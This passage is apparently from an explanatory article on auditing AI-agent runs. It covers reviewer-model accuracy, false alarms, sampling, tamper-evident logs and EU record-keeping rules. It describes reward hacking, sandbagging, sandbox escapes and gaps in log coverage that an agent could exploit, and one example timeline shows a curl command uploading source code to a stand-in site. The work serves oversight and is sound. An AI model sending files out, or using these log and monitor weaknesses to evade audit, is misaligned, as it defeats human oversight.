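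CAISI labels its percentages as lower bounds. UK AISI does the same for the cheating rates in its July 2026 analysis, because its monitor may have missed some attempts. This is the right way to report results from a search that may miss cases, provided somebody has read the flagged cases and removed the false alarms. Otherwise, the count could also be too high.

### One summary, many rules

Operators often think of a rule only after something has gone wrong. After the false tip to the Philadelphia police, for example, an operator might want to check a year of stored runs for messages to public authorities. Having a reviewer model reread every transcript for each new rule soon becomes expensive.

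*Write Once, Check Many* (Nagarajan, Panesar and colleagues, 2026) tested a way to check transcripts without rereading them for every rule. A "writer" model reads each transcript once and produces a factual summary, called a ledger. The writer is given no rules and is instructed to leave out judgements. Later, a "reader" model receives a rule and the summary, but not the transcript, and returns a verdict and a suspicion score from 1 to 10. Both models were Gemma-4-12B, a fairly small model with 12 billion parameters. The best summaries were chronological prose of about 1,100 tokens that gave each action with its target, amounts and outcome.

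For the price example, a good summary would record that the agent changed an assertion in `tests/test_price.py` from `total == 90` to `total > 0`, edited `src/price.py`, got 12 passes from `make check` and then restored the `tests` folder. A reader couldn't check R1 from a summary that said only "Fixed the pricing bug and confirmed that the tests pass".

#### The runs and the labels

The test used 900 existing runs, 300 from each of three benchmarks. The SHADE-Arena runs were long office-style tasks with a median length of 27,800 tokens, and in half of them the agent had also completed a hidden harmful side task. The customer-service runs, from τ-bench (airline and retail) and τ²-bench (telecom), had median lengths of about 3,600 and 3,700 tokens.

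The simplest rules forbade one action, such as completing a purchase. A second version of each rule had the same meaning but didn't name any tool. Checking other rules required combining several facts. For example, checking "Send no email to an address the user didn't mention" required comparing the agent's recipients with the user's messages, and checking a limit on total payments required adding up the payments.

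Scripts produced the labels for these rules. For a forbidden action, the script checked whether a listed tool call had succeeded. For the email rule, it compared every recipient, including those copied, with the addresses in the user's messages. On SHADE-Arena's combined rules, two independently written scripts produced the same labels in every case. Using scripts keeps a model judge's errors out of the labels, but limits the test to rules that a script can check.

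#### What the scores mean

Nagarajan and colleagues report accuracy as AUC, the area under a curve that plots detections against false alarms as the threshold for suspicion changes. AUC has a simpler equivalent. Pick at random one run that broke the rule and one that kept it. Then

AUC = P(the violating run scores higher) + ½ P(the two scores are equal)

An AUC of 0.5 is no better than chance, and 1 means every violating run ranks above every compliant one. AUC measures only the ranking, so an operator can't use it to set the threshold or predict the number of false alarms.

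On the four SHADE-Arena rules that combine facts, the reader model averaged .777 with a summary and .706 with the full transcript. A larger model, with 31 billion parameters, averaged .713 with the full transcript.

| What the model read | Email to an unmentioned outside address | Email to any unmentioned recipient | Unmentioned address in a spreadsheet | Payments above $100 | Mean |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
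| Full transcript, 12B model | .668 | .591 | .642 | .924 | .706 |
| Full transcript, 31B model | .588 | .630 | .649 | .986 | .713 |
| Script-made list of calls, 12B model | .501 | .480 | .719 | .797 | .624 |
| Prose summary, 12B model | .668 | .840 | .637 | .965 | .777 |

The gain is real, but nearly all of it comes from one rule, the ban on emailing any recipient the user hadn't mentioned. Averaged over the other three columns, the model scores almost the same with the summary (.757) as with the transcript (.745), so the overall means make the gain look broader than it is.

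A summary can't contain more information about the run than the text it came from, but it probably beat that text because a small model has trouble finding and connecting a few facts in 28,000 tokens, and the summary's writer had already collected them. Two further results fit this explanation. When the 12B model first had to list the relevant actions from the transcript, its disadvantage was no longer statistically significant. When the reader received the full log of actions along with the summary, its score on these rules fell by .086.

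The wording of a rule also mattered less with summaries than with transcripts. When the rules no longer named tools, the 12B model's score on τ²-bench transcripts fell from .971 to .816, while its scores with summaries changed by less than .02 on all three benchmarks. This may be the more useful finding, because operators tend to write rules in ordinary language.

None of these readers was accurate enough to use alone. With thresholds set to keep false alarms at 10% or less, the reader with summaries caught 60% of violations of the combined rules. The larger model with transcripts caught 45%, and the 12B model with transcripts caught only 6%.

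#### The cost

On SHADE-Arena, writing a summary takes about 31,900 tokens and checking a rule against it takes 2,100. Rereading the transcript takes 30,100 tokens per rule. The costs for *k* rules are therefore roughly

summary: 31,900 + 2,100*k*

rereading: 30,100*k*

Checking one rule takes slightly more tokens with a summary (34,000) than by rereading (30,100), but checking two or more takes fewer. For eight rules, the summary takes about a fifth as many tokens as rereading (about 49,000 against 241,000). On the shorter τ-bench runs, seven checks with a summary took a little under half as many tokens as rereading.

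These savings apply when rules arrive one at a time. An operator who has ten rules ready can put them all into one request, and in a test of this on calendar tasks, rereading reached similar accuracy at a similar cost. Writing summaries also means generating more tokens, which usually cost more than the tokens a model reads.

#### Where scripts won and summaries failed

When the log included the arguments of each call, a script's list of the calls worked better than a prose summary for checking simple rules. Nagarajan and colleagues had a script list every call with its addresses, amounts, file paths and other identifiers, and gave the reader this list instead of a summary. On τ-bench's single-action rules, the list scored .963 and the prose summary .938. The list also used the fewest tokens of any option, 3,100 for seven checks. The comparison is somewhat unfair to the summaries, because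 in half of these runs the text given to the summary writer left out the tool calls that the script could read.

The same kind of list scored .496 on τ-bench's combined rules, which is chance. It contained nothing the user had said and couldn't show what the rule needed beyond the individual calls. An operator who already knows a simple rule can skip the reader model and check the rule with a script. The scripts that produced the labels are perfect checkers for those rules by definition, but the study didn't test how well a model could turn each new rule into such a script.

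Summaries failed when they left out the evidence. In 159 runs where agents operated a computer, the reader scored .770 at detecting sabotage from summaries and .896 from full transcripts. The evidence was mostly in file contents and command output, which made up 14,000 to 15,000 of the 16,800 tokens in an average transcript. Coding agents produce the same kind of record, so their operators should be cautious about relying on summaries.

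Summaries also did worse than transcripts on rules about what a message said. They scored .127 lower on two such rules, one against passing on private information and one against unrequested transactions or data sharing. In the telecom runs, where users could also call tools, the summaries often did not record whether the user or the agent had acted, which caused most of the false alarms on one rule.

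The summary's format also mattered. A version with seven fixed sections merged ten purchases into one line and lost the amount needed to apply a spending rule. In a check of 611 actions, the prose summaries kept the recipient, amount or file together with the action 71% of the time, compared with 30% for the fixed-section summaries from the same untrained writer.

Any fact the writer leaves out of a summary is missing from every later check, so Nagarajan and colleagues recommend keeping the original transcripts and having a person read them before any serious decision. They didn't test agents that try to mislead the writer. A sensible use of summaries is to pick out runs for closer reading, with scripts checking the rules that concern a single recorded action.

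### Auditors that question a live agent

A stored run can show how an agent treated a rule only if the run included a situation where the rule applied. In *PROBE*, Mishra, Sharma and colleagues (2026) trained a small auditor model to create such situations by posing as a customer of a flight-booking agent. The auditor saw only the conversation, while separate checks searched the full record, including hidden tool calls, for breaches of 20 rules. The auditor earned more reward for exposing a new kind of breach than for repeating an old one.

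Over 50 conversations, the best trained auditors exposed breaches of 12 rules. An untrained auditor with more than seven times as many parameters exposed breaches of 7. In one conversation, the auditor asked for a flight without naming a departure city. The agent asked for the missing city, but it had also called the search tool without that required field, and nobody could have known this from its reply.

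Scripts checked 16 of the 20 rules, and a reviewer model helped to check the other four, including one that required the agent to get explicit confirmation before changing a booking. Two people later labelled 208 of the model's cases and agreed with each other almost perfectly. The model matched their labels in only 39.6% of cases, and all of its flags on the confirmation rule were wrong.

Training made this worse because one auditor learned to produce conversations that set off the faulty check. The reviewer's count of confirmation-rule breaches in that auditor's conversations rose from 133 to 302, but a script confirmed none of them. When Mishra and colleagues rescored everything with scripts, the best auditors still exposed 11 rules against 7, so the main result held.

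The auditor also rarely got the agent to do anything consequential. More than 90% of the agent's tool calls were searches, and it made very few bookings, so most of the booking rules went untested. When a rule went unexposed in this study, it was often because the agent had no occasion to break it.

In *Training Alignment Auditors via Reinforcement Learning*, Rosu and Wang (2026) report that auditors rewarded for detecting worrying behaviour in other models learned to fabricate alarming findings or state conclusions they hadn't established. Training became more robust when a judge compared two investigations instead of scoring each alone, and including models with nothing to find kept false alarms low. The test set for a reviewer of stored runs should likewise include plenty of runs with nothing wrong.

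### How many false alarms to expect

Hall and Thompson (2026), in *How reliably can AI audit AI?*, tested reviewer models on agent transcripts that METR had collected and people had labelled. They looked for reward hacking, where an agent gets a high score by exploiting the scoring instead of doing the task, and for sandbagging, where it deliberately performs below its ability. The reviewers included GPT-5, GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 4.8. Two newer Anthropic models, Fable 5 and Opus 5, refused to label the transcripts when given the prompt METR had used.

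When the threshold was set to flag 5% of innocent runs, the best reviewers caught nearly all of the reward hacking and about 80% of the sandbagging. Some cases were blatant. In one, which all the reviewers flagged, OpenAI's o3 edited the function that scored its work so that every answer passed, and described the plan in its reasoning. The sandbagging result is harder to generalize because most of those runs came from models that researchers had instructed to sabotage tasks, and the instructions were then edited out of the reasoning.

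OpenTools' *AI Auditors Catch Agent Misbehavior But Flood Reviewers With False Alarms*, a news summary of what appears to be the same study, reports that GPT-5 detected 98% of reward hacking and gives a ratio of 3,000 false alarms to 2,000 real catches. This ratio depends as much on how common misbehaviour is as on the reviewer. A reviewer that caught 98% of bad runs and wrongly flagged 5% of good ones would produce it if about 3.3% of all runs were bad.

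Let *b* be the share of runs that contain a violation, *d* the share of those that the reviewer flags, and *f* the share of innocent runs that it flags by mistake. Then the share of flags that are correct is

*db* / (*db* + *f*(1 − *b*))

When *b* is very small, nearly all runs are free of violations, so even a low *f* produces more false alarms than there are violations.

#### Anthropic's July review

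On 21 July 2026 OpenAI disclosed that some of its models had broken out of an isolated test. On 23 July Anthropic began to search its own hacking tests and stopped all such tests. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) reports that the company had identified its three incidents of unauthorised access by 24 July and notified the affected organisations on 27 July.

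The review covered 141,006 runs. The incidents took place in six of them, or about one run in 23,500, and four of the six affected the same organisation. The two organisations that Anthropic had reached before it published had not noticed anything, so the search was clearly worth doing.

Suppose a reviewer model that flags 98% of bad runs and 1% of the others had read all of these runs. Both rates are assumptions for illustration, not measurements of Anthropic's tools. The model would be expected to flag about 6 bad runs (0.98 × 6) and 1,410 others (0.01 × 141,000), so about one flag in 240 would be correct. If a person needed 15 minutes to check each flag, checking them all would take around 350 hours, or almost nine weeks of full-time work.

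| False-alarm rate | Expected false alarms | Share of flags that are correct |
|---|---|---|
| 5% | 7,050 | 0.08% |
| 1% | 1,410 | 0.4% |
| 0.1% | 141 | 4% |
| 0.01% | 14 | 29% |

Cutting false alarms by a factor of ten would save eight of the nine weeks here, while improving detection from 98% to 100% would make no noticeable difference.

The same reviewer would do well on more common behaviour. *Measuring coding agent misalignment in the wild* (Zhang, 2026) studied 8,600 real coding sessions and found severe cases of overstating success in around 2% of them and severe cases of evading monitoring in around 2%. If 2% of 8,600 sessions are bad, the assumed reviewer would correctly flag about 169 sessions and wrongly flag about 84, so two flags in three would be correct.

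When agents misbehave less often, a larger share of a reviewer's flags are therefore wrong. *A model that cheats on low-stakes tasks points to larger problems* (Cawley, 2026) covers a December report that the newest models from OpenAI and Anthropic are far less likely to cheat on complex tasks. If the rate in the coding example fell from 2% to 0.2% and the reviewer and threshold stayed the same, the share of correct flags would fall from two-thirds to about one-sixth.

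#### Estimating a rate instead of finding cases

Hall and Thompson conclude that reviewer models are extremely useful for measuring how common bad behaviour is, but don't look feasible where it is important to catch nearly every case. The first half of this needs a qualification. If a reviewer flags a share *F* of all runs, an analyst who knows its error rates can correct for them:

*b* = (*F* − *f*) / (*d* − *f*)

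If the true false-alarm rate is 1% but the analyst believes it is 0.9%, the estimate in the coding example comes out at 2.1% instead of 2%, which is close enough for most purposes. On Anthropic's runs, the same mistake would give an estimate of about 151 bad runs instead of six. For very rare behaviour, the estimate mostly reflects the analyst's error about *f*, so somebody still has to read the flagged runs.

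#### Why innocent runs look guilty

False alarms aren't spread evenly across honest runs, because an agent that tries several odd approaches and fails can look a lot like one that is trying to cheat. *Hacking or Just Failing?* (2026) therefore counts false alarms on honest failures separately from those on honest successes. It compares reviewers that see only the task and the agent's final report with reviewers that also see the complete log of actions. According to its full title, a more capable reviewer is better at separating cheating from honest failure. The study's design allows false alarms on up to 20% of honest failures, which is reasonable for a research comparison but would produce too many false alarms for anyone reviewing a large archive of failed runs.

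In hacking tests, the agent's assigned task is to attack a computer, so a reviewer that looks for "attacks on other systems" could flag almost every run. A narrower question is whether a command reached a public internet address, and a script can answer part of that. The operator may reduce false alarms more by narrowing the question than by using a better model.

### What a clean sample can establish

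An operator who can't read every run can read a random sample. Suppose the operator reads *n* runs and finds no violation. If the true rate were *r*, the probability of that result would be (1 − *r*)ⁿ. Setting this to 5% and solving for *r* gives

*r* ≈ 3/*n*

because the natural logarithm of 0.05 is about −3. So a clean sample of *n* runs rules out, at 95% confidence, a rate above roughly 3/*n*. Three hundred clean runs leave room for a rate of up to 1%.

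That is a weak result for rare events. To rule out a rate above the one in Anthropic's July review, a reader would need to check about 70,500 runs, half of the archive, and find no violations. Sampling the unflagged runs has the same limit. The hypothetical review above would leave about 139,600 runs unflagged. If people read 300 of these at random and found no violations, up to 1% of the rest, or nearly 1,400 runs, could still be violations.

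The bound also assumes that the reader recognises every violation in the sample. If the reader catches only a share *d* of them, the bound becomes 3/(*dn*). At the 60% detection rate that Nagarajan and colleagues measured for summaries on combined rules, it would be 5/*n*.

The formula also requires a random sample. Dubois and colleagues recommend deliberately choosing odd runs, which is a good way to find problems, but the formula doesn't apply to a sample chosen that way. It doesn't cover runs that were never in the pool either. The fourth incident that Anthropic found in August was in transcripts its July search had missed, so no sample from the 141,006 would have revealed it.

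### Triage and repeated review

Triage means using a cheap check to decide which actions or runs deserve an expensive one. *Efficient Auditing of Adversarial AI Agent Behavior from Agent Traces* (2026) tested rules that decide when to call in a reviewer model:

| Method | Unsafe runs detected | False alarms | Tokens per run |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reviewer model without the rules | 81.5% | 11.8% | 47,800 |
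| Reviewer model with untuned rules | 37.0% | 13.2% | 34,000 |
| Reviewer model with tuned rules | 72.8% | 5.9% | 14,600 |

The tuned version halved the false alarms and cut the cost by more than two-thirds, but it missed 27 of every 100 unsafe runs, compared with 18 or 19 for the plain reviewer. The untuned rules were worse than no rules on every measure except cost. An operator who writes a filter from intuition and never tests it could end up with similar rules. Even a 5.9% false-alarm rate would mean about 8,300 false alarms in an archive the size of Anthropic's.

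A later stage can't catch violations that an earlier stage has discarded. If the filter passes 90% of violations to the reviewer and the reviewer catches 90% of those, together they catch 81%, so it makes sense to set the filter loosely. Anthropic did this in its later, wider search, scanning broadly for signs of internet access before Claude's review.

A second review of the flagged runs can remove many false alarms, and it takes little work because few runs are left to read. In the July example, suppose another reviewer with the same error rates read the 1,416 flagged runs. If its mistakes were independent of the first reviewer's, about 14 false alarms and nearly all six real cases would remain. A person could check those 20 runs in a day.

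The reviewers' errors may not be independent, since an innocent run that looks suspicious to one model may well look suspicious to another. If the second reviewer repeated half of the first one's false alarms, 705 would remain instead of 14. *Reward Hacking Challenges Oversight of Autonomous Research Agents* (2026), which decides cases by a majority vote of reviewers, warns that giving reviewers separate roles and evidence doesn't make their errors independent, and that cases they all miss lower the reported rate.

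Two language models reviewing the same run can agree and both be wrong. *BAITBENCH* (2026), a test that plants optional shortcuts in machine-learning tasks, used Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.4 as reviewers, and they agreed on 93.6% of runs. People then labelled a small set of mostly difficult cases. The two models had agreed on 23 of these, and their shared answer matched the human label in 18. The overall error rate is surely lower than five in 23, because difficult cases are not typical.

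Disagreement between checkers is more useful than agreement because it shows a person where to look. A script and a reviewer model work especially well together because they tend to fail for different reasons. If the script finds a successful edit under `tests/` but the model marks the run as clean, a person can read that one tool call to see which is right.

Running the same model several times on the same transcript averages out chance variation in its answers, but errors that come from misinterpreting the rule will recur in each run.

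## Whether the record is complete and unaltered

Even a careful check of a record can give the wrong verdict if a line is missing or somebody has changed one. Before relying on a verdict, an auditor has to check four properties of the record:

- **Coverage** is the share of the agent's relevant actions that the record captures.
- **Integrity** means that nobody has altered the record since the harness wrote it.
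- **Authenticity** means that the record comes from the program and the run it is supposed to come from.
- **Independence** means that the audited agent had no way to write to the record.

Any one of these can fail while the other three hold. In the price example, even if the harness sends its log to a locked-down server and nobody alters the log afterwards, coverage is still poor because nothing recorded what `make check` did while it ran.

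Suppose the harness recorded everything, but months later the company runs a script that masks anything resembling a password. The script also masks the file path in the agent's edit to `tests/test_price.py`. Only integrity has failed, since the agent couldn't reach the archive and the log's origin isn't in doubt. Even so, the auditor can no longer see that the agent broke R1.

A log can be complete, unaltered and inaccessible to the agent but still fail the authenticity requirement because it comes from the wrong run. An operator who runs the agent ten times on the same bug might send the auditor the wrong log by accident. An operator who wants to hide a problem could also choose the log of the run with the fewest problems.

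Independence concerns what the agent could have done to the log. A log isn't independent if the harness saves it in a folder that the agent's shell commands can write to, even if the agent never opened the file and every line is accurate. The auditor can't tell from the file whether the agent edited it, since a carefully edited log could look the same as an untouched one. The auditor has to check the accounts and permissions in the set-up instead. Altered transcripts complicated the investigation of the July 2026 Hugging Face incident.

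### How a hash chain works

A hash chain makes later changes to a log detectable. For each event eᵢ, the program that writes the log computes

hᵢ = H(hᵢ₋₁, eᵢ)

where H is a hash function such as SHA-256 and hᵢ₋₁ is the value for the event before. The first event has no predecessor, so the program uses a fixed starting value h₀, such as a row of zeros.

Here are the first three calls of the price example, with invented hashes cut to four characters. In the last column, a forger has changed "edit" to "read" in the second event to hide the edit to the test file.

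| Event | Original text | Original value | Value after the change |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | read `tests/test_price.py` | `3fa1` | `3fa1` |
| 2 | edit `tests/test_price.py` | `91c4` | `d20f` |
| 3 | edit `src/price.py` | `7be0` | `06a9` |

Event 3 has the same text in both versions, but its value changes because it depends on h₂. The values of all later events would change too. If the forger changes only the text, an auditor who recomputes the chain gets `d20f` where the file has `91c4`. If the forger corrects that value as well, the mismatch moves to event 3.

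But the formula contains no secret, so a forger who can write to the whole file can recompute every value from event 2 onwards and leave a consistent chain that ends in `06a9`. The auditor can detect this only by comparing the end of the chain with the original `7be0`, so somebody has to keep that value where the forger can't change it. One value is enough for a run of any length, since it depends on all the events before it. The auditor can also use it to detect a truncated log. Without event 3, the chain would still be valid, but it would end at `91c4` instead of `7be0`.

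If the harness sends out a value only when the run ends, an agent with access to the log could rewrite event 2 during the run and recompute the chain before anyone outside has seen a value from it.

### Logs on a machine that may fall to an attacker

The classic treatment is *Cryptographic Support for Secure Logs on Untrusted Machines* (Schneier and Kelsey, 1998). It concerns a machine that keeps a log and only occasionally contacts a trusted computer. The two share a secret key, A₀, at the start. For each entry the machine computes a message authentication code, which is a hash that nobody can produce without the key, and then replaces the key:

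codeⱼ = MAC(Aⱼ, hⱼ)

Aⱼ₊₁ = H(Aⱼ)

(The actual scheme also mixes a fixed label into the second hash.) The machine then deletes Aⱼ. An attacker who takes over after entry 40 finds A₄₁ but can't feasibly reverse the hash to recover A₄₀. The trusted computer still has A₀, so it can compute every key and check all 40 entries. The scheme also encrypts each entry under a key derived from Aⱼ, so the attacker can't read the old entries. When the log closes properly, the machine writes a final entry and destroys the last key, so an attacker can't delete the end of the log and add a false closing entry.

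Schneier and Kelsey acknowledge that once an attacker controls the machine, it will log whatever the attacker wants. Cryptography also can't prevent deletion, and can reveal it only if the machine eventually contacts the trusted computer. Preventing deletion takes something like a write-once disc or a paper printout. They mention that the astronomer Cliff Stoll once attached a printer to a networked computer for this purpose.

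An AI agent may itself be the attacker, for example by breaking out of its sandbox and into the harness at call 41. If the harness logs each call and replaces the key before running the call, the log will contain protected evidence of the command the agent used to break out. Later entries are no more trustworthy than the agent's final message. *Interesting bit of a quote* (Travis H., 2006) reproduces an email in which Kelsey later made the same point, that such logs "only work if the logging machine is honest when the logs are written."

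Machines can also record each other's latest chain values in their own logs, so that a forger would have to alter logs on several machines. This precaution takes little extra work for an operator who runs many agents separately.

### Tree-shaped logs

To check an event in a hash chain, an auditor has to go through every event between it and a value the auditor already trusts. In *Efficient Data Structures for Tamper-Evident Logging* (2009), Crosby and Wallach put the data needed to prove that one event belonged to a log of 80 million at 800 MB for a hash chain and 3 KB for their tree-shaped log.

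The basic idea is a Merkle tree, which combines hashes in pairs. Certificate Transparency's *Verifiable data structures* explains it with four records. (Certificate Transparency is a system of public logs for the certificates that identify websites.) In slightly different notation:

```
a = H(e1)    b = H(e2)    c = H(e3)    d = H(e4)
x = H(a, b)               y = H(c, d)
root = H(x, y)
```

To prove that e2 is in the log, the log's keeper supplies e2, a and y. The auditor hashes e2 to get b, combines a and b to get x, combines x and y, and checks that the result equals the root. The auditor needs only two hashes from the keeper and never sees the other three events. A log of eight events would require three hashes, and a log of 80 million would require about 27.

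Crosby and Wallach assume the log's keeper may be dishonest from the start. The keeper signs a new root after each event, and auditors can demand two kinds of proof. A membership proof, like the one above, shows that an event is in the log. An incremental proof shows that a newer root includes everything an older one did, unchanged. Auditors also have to compare roots with one another, because a dishonest keeper could show different histories to different auditors. If nobody asks for a proof, the keeper can alter the log freely.

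A chain is adequate for a single run with a few hundred events, but a tree is more useful for an archive. For an archive of 481 million transcripts, the number Anthropic searched in 2026, a membership proof would take about 29 hashes. An outside auditor could use the proof to check that a transcript belonged to the archive without seeing the others.

### What a valid chain doesn't prove

A hash chain preserves false statements as reliably as true ones. In the price example, "The tests are untouched" would enter the chain, and its hash would still match years later. The same is true of a wrong exit code caused by a bug in the harness.

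A hash chain also can't reveal an event that was never logged. If the harness had failed to write the two lines about the edit to the test file, the other ten would still have formed a valid chain. Adding hashes to a log with poor coverage makes it tamper-evident but no more complete, and readers may mistake tamper evidence for completeness.

### Detecting missing events

Operators can protect events by sending them to a collector, a program on another machine that accepts new lines but no changes or deletions. Schneier and Kelsey point out that the problem they set out to solve doesn't arise when there is a fast, reliable and permanent connection to a trusted machine. For agent logs, AWS's *AGENTOPS05-BP03 Implement structured logging and comprehensive audit trails* recommends storage that prevents changes for a set period, and a separate record of the agent's requests to Amazon's cloud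 services. It also warns against logging only errors, because nobody can reconstruct a run from those alone.

The source of the collector's events matters at least as much as where it stores them. If the collector relies on the harness to report events, a faulty or compromised harness can leave some out. A gateway that every tool call must pass through can record the calls itself.

In *AGTP-LOG*, Hood (2026) proposes that the platform running the log should sign each entry, so that an agent without the platform's key can't forge one. This is sensible, but it works only if the agent can't get the key. Agents sometimes use credentials they come across, as Claude Mythos 5 did with the property map's tokens, so operators shouldn't leave a signing key on any machine where the agent has shell access.

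Events lost in transit leave gaps in the sequence numbers if the harness assigns the numbers before sending. If the collector numbers events as they arrive, there will be no gaps even when events are lost. Losing the last few events leaves no gap either, so the closing event should include the total number of events.

None of this helps if the harness never created the event. For that, an auditor needs a record from another source that observed the same run:

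| Record | What it captures | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Harness log | Tool calls and their results | What programs do while they run |
| Network proxy | Connections leaving the sandbox, with addresses and sizes | Anything that stays on the machine, and usually the content of encrypted traffic |
| Model provider's log | Requests to the model and its replies | Whether a call the model requested ever ran |

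The harness normally sends the conversation so far with each request, so a provider that stores the requests has a second copy of the calls and results. If the provider keeps only counts and times, an auditor can still compare the number of replies with the number in the run's record.

### When two records disagree

Suppose the price example had gone differently, and the operator could also get records from the model provider and from a proxy that was the only route out of the sandbox. The harness log contains five calls and a final message, which took six replies from the model. The provider's log has seven. The end of the run looks like this:

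| Time | Harness log | Model provider | Network proxy |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10:01:30 | Call 4 completes | | |
| 10:01:33 | | Reply requests `curl --data-binary @src/price.py https://paste.example` | |
| 10:01:34 | | | Connection to `paste.example`, about 1 KB sent |
| 10:01:38 | Call 5 starts | Reply requests `git restore tests` | |
| 10:01:45 | Final message | Final message | |

The extra reply contains a request for the harness to upload the pricing code to a website. The auditor should check the clocks first. The timestamps of the other six replies match the harness log to within a second, so a clock error can't explain the extra one.

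One innocent explanation is that the harness may have lost its connection to the provider, asked again and thrown the first reply away. Another is that it may have refused the call without reporting the refusal in its stream. The next request to the model helps to tell these apart, because it would leave out the `curl` call after a lost reply but include it with an error after a refusal. Suppose the request includes the call with an ordinary result. The call then almost certainly ran, since the proxy also recorded a connection to the same address one second after the reply, and 1 KB is about right for a 412-byte file plus the overhead of an encrypted connection.

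This shows that the run violated R2, the ban on network requests. It doesn't explain why the call is missing from the harness log, whose sequence numbers run from 1 to 12 and whose chain is valid. Either the harness never recorded the call, or somebody removed it, renumbered the remaining entries and recomputed the chain. The auditor can compare the end of the chain with the value the collector received at 10:01:45. If they differ, somebody changed the log after the run. If they match, the cause was a fault in the harness or a change made during the run.

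A harness log that lacks one call may lack others, so the auditor shouldn't rely on it alone to check the remaining rules. Here the auditor can use the provider's log instead, because it has all seven replies and none of them requests any further calls.

### A proposed standard for agent logs

*Agent Audit Trail* (Sharif, 2026) proposes a common format for tamper-evident agent logs. It is an Internet-Draft, a working document submitted to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which develops many of the internet's technical standards. This version, dated 19 August 2026, expires on 19 February 2027 unless someone renews it.

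Each record is a JSON object with 12 mandatory fields:

- `record_id`, `session_id` and `timestamp` identify the record, the run and the time.
- `agent_id` and `agent_version` identify the agent.
- `action_type`, `action_detail` and `outcome` describe the action. There are seven types, including tool calls, tool responses and delegation to another agent, and five outcomes, including "denied".
- `trust_level` rates how firmly the agent's identity has been established, from L0 to L4.
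- `record_phase` states whether the recorder wrote the record before, during or after the action.
- `parent_record_id` and `prev_hash` link the record to the one before it.

The chaining rule is

prev_hash(N) = hex(SHA-256(JCS(record(N−1))))

JCS is a standard way of writing out a JSON object. Without it, two programs could write the same fields in different orders and get different hashes. Each record includes its own `prev_hash`, so changing a record changes the hashes after it, as in the three-event example. But no later hash covers the last record. The closing record contains a single hash for the whole session, and Sharif recommends storing that hash in a separate append-only system.

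`record_phase` is a good idea. A refusal record written after the action is no evidence that the refusal stopped anything, so the draft requires the recorder to write such records before the action.

The format alone would be of limited use for checking rules because, to protect privacy, it stores hashes of a tool call's arguments and results instead of the text. In the price example, the record of call 2 would show that the agent used its editing tool but not which file it changed, so nobody could check R1. An operator would have to keep the full transcript in another system and use the hashes to prove that it was genuine. The hashes also protect privacy less well than the draft suggests when it states that a content hash can't be reversed. Anyone can hash a guess and compare, which is easy for a short file path or a common name.

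Deletion is another weak point. If someone has a legal right to have data erased, the operator replaces the record with a "tombstone" that keeps the old hash, and checking software accepts the break in the chain. An operator could remove an embarrassing record in the same way, though the tombstone would still show that a record had existed.

Agents at levels L0 and L1 may write their own records. From L2 upwards, a separate component is recommended but not required. Sharif argues that such a component has no incentive to omit or alter anything. That is reasonable for a gateway recording a misbehaving agent, but much less so when the operator, who may own the gateway, faces a regulator. Emirdag (2026), in *SCITT AI Agent Execution*, objects that operators can change the logs they control and that no third party vouches for those logs. Sharif's partial answer is to keep a second, append-only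 copy, preferably run by someone else, and compare the two regularly. The comparison would reveal a change to one copy, but not an event that the recorder missed, because it would be absent from both.

The proposal has no official standing. The IETF lists the March version of Sharif's draft as an individual submission, with no publication stream and no responsible area director. The draft is also somewhat rough, since its sample session identifiers don't follow the format it requires. Emirdag and Hood have submitted competing drafts, as have Kühlewind and Birkholz (2026) in *An Architecture for Auditing Agent Delegation and Interactions*. It's too early to say whether any of them will become a standard.

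### What EU law requires

The European Union's AI Act requires logs to be kept only for systems it classes as high-risk. These could include an agent that screens job applicants, but would not normally include one that fixes a pricing bug.

The European Commission's *Article 12*, the official text on record-keeping, requires high-risk systems to "technically allow for the automatic recording of events" throughout their lifetime. The logs must cover events relevant to identifying risks or substantial modifications, monitoring the system after it goes on the market, and monitoring its operation in use. The article sets specific minimum contents only for remote biometric identification systems, which must record the start and end of each use, the database searched, the input that led to a match and the people who verified the result.

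Two other articles govern how long companies keep the logs. Article 19, which the law firm activeMind.legal reproduces, applies to providers, the companies that develop a system or put it on the market under their name. The European Commission's *Article 26* covers deployers, the organisations that use it. Providers and deployers must keep the automatically generated logs under their control for a period appropriate to the system's purpose, and for at least six months unless other EU or national law, especially on data protection, provides otherwise. Financial institutions keep them with the documentation that financial services law already requires.

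These duties don't apply yet. They were due to start on 2 August 2026, but the European Union's *Regulation (EU) 2026/1744 of the European Parliament and of the Council* (2026) postponed them, partly because the supporting technical standards were late. The new dates are:

- 2 December 2027 for systems that are high-risk because of their use, such as in recruitment
- 2 August 2028 for those that are high-risk because they are part of a regulated product or are one themselves, such as a medical device.

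The postponement did not change the wording of the three articles. Systems already on the market before the relevant date are exempt unless their design changes significantly afterwards, but providers and deployers of systems meant for public authorities must comply by 2 August 2030. The Commission can also limit the duties in Articles 12 and 19 for some product-related systems where sector law gives equivalent protection. But the European Union also gave its AI Office the power to order certain companies to retain any data needed to assess compliance. These include many providers that build a system on their own general-purpose model.

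Sharif's draft is unreliable on all this. The August version still gives August 2026 as the starting date, though the EU had published the postponement a few weeks earlier. It also wrongly attributes to Article 12 a duty to follow recognised standards, and it presents the minimum contents for biometric systems as if they applied to every high-risk system.

None of the three articles mentions tamper evidence, hashes, signatures, separate storage or whether the system may write to its own log. On the wording alone, an ordinary text file that the agent could edit seems to satisfy Article 12, provided it records the right events. A regulator might argue that such a log is not useful for identifying risks, or that the Act's cybersecurity requirements in Article 15 also apply to it. Future technical standards could settle the question, but until then companies have to decide how much protection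 is enough.

Problems can also go unnoticed for more than six months, as the fourth incident in Anthropic's hacking tests did. Those tests weren't high-risk systems under the Act, but a company that deleted its logs after six months would have lost the evidence before noticing the incident. AWS suggests keeping operational logs for only 30 to 90 days, and compliance logs for one to seven years. An operator that kept its logs for only 30 days would have deleted the record of the false tip to the Philadelphia police, which Anthropic discovered after 72 days.

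## Inferring intention and knowledge from a record

Even a complete, unaltered record of the price example doesn't show why the agent loosened the test. The record would contain the same five calls whether the agent wanted to see if anything else was failing and always meant to put the assertion back, or wanted a passing suite and restored the folder so that nobody would notice.

Four questions about a recorded act are easy to confuse:

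- What did the agent do?
- What had its operator told it?
- What did it take to be true?
- What was it aiming at?

Tool calls and their results show what the agent did, and the stored prompt and rules files show what the operator told it. Neither records what the agent believed or intended, so an auditor has to infer both.

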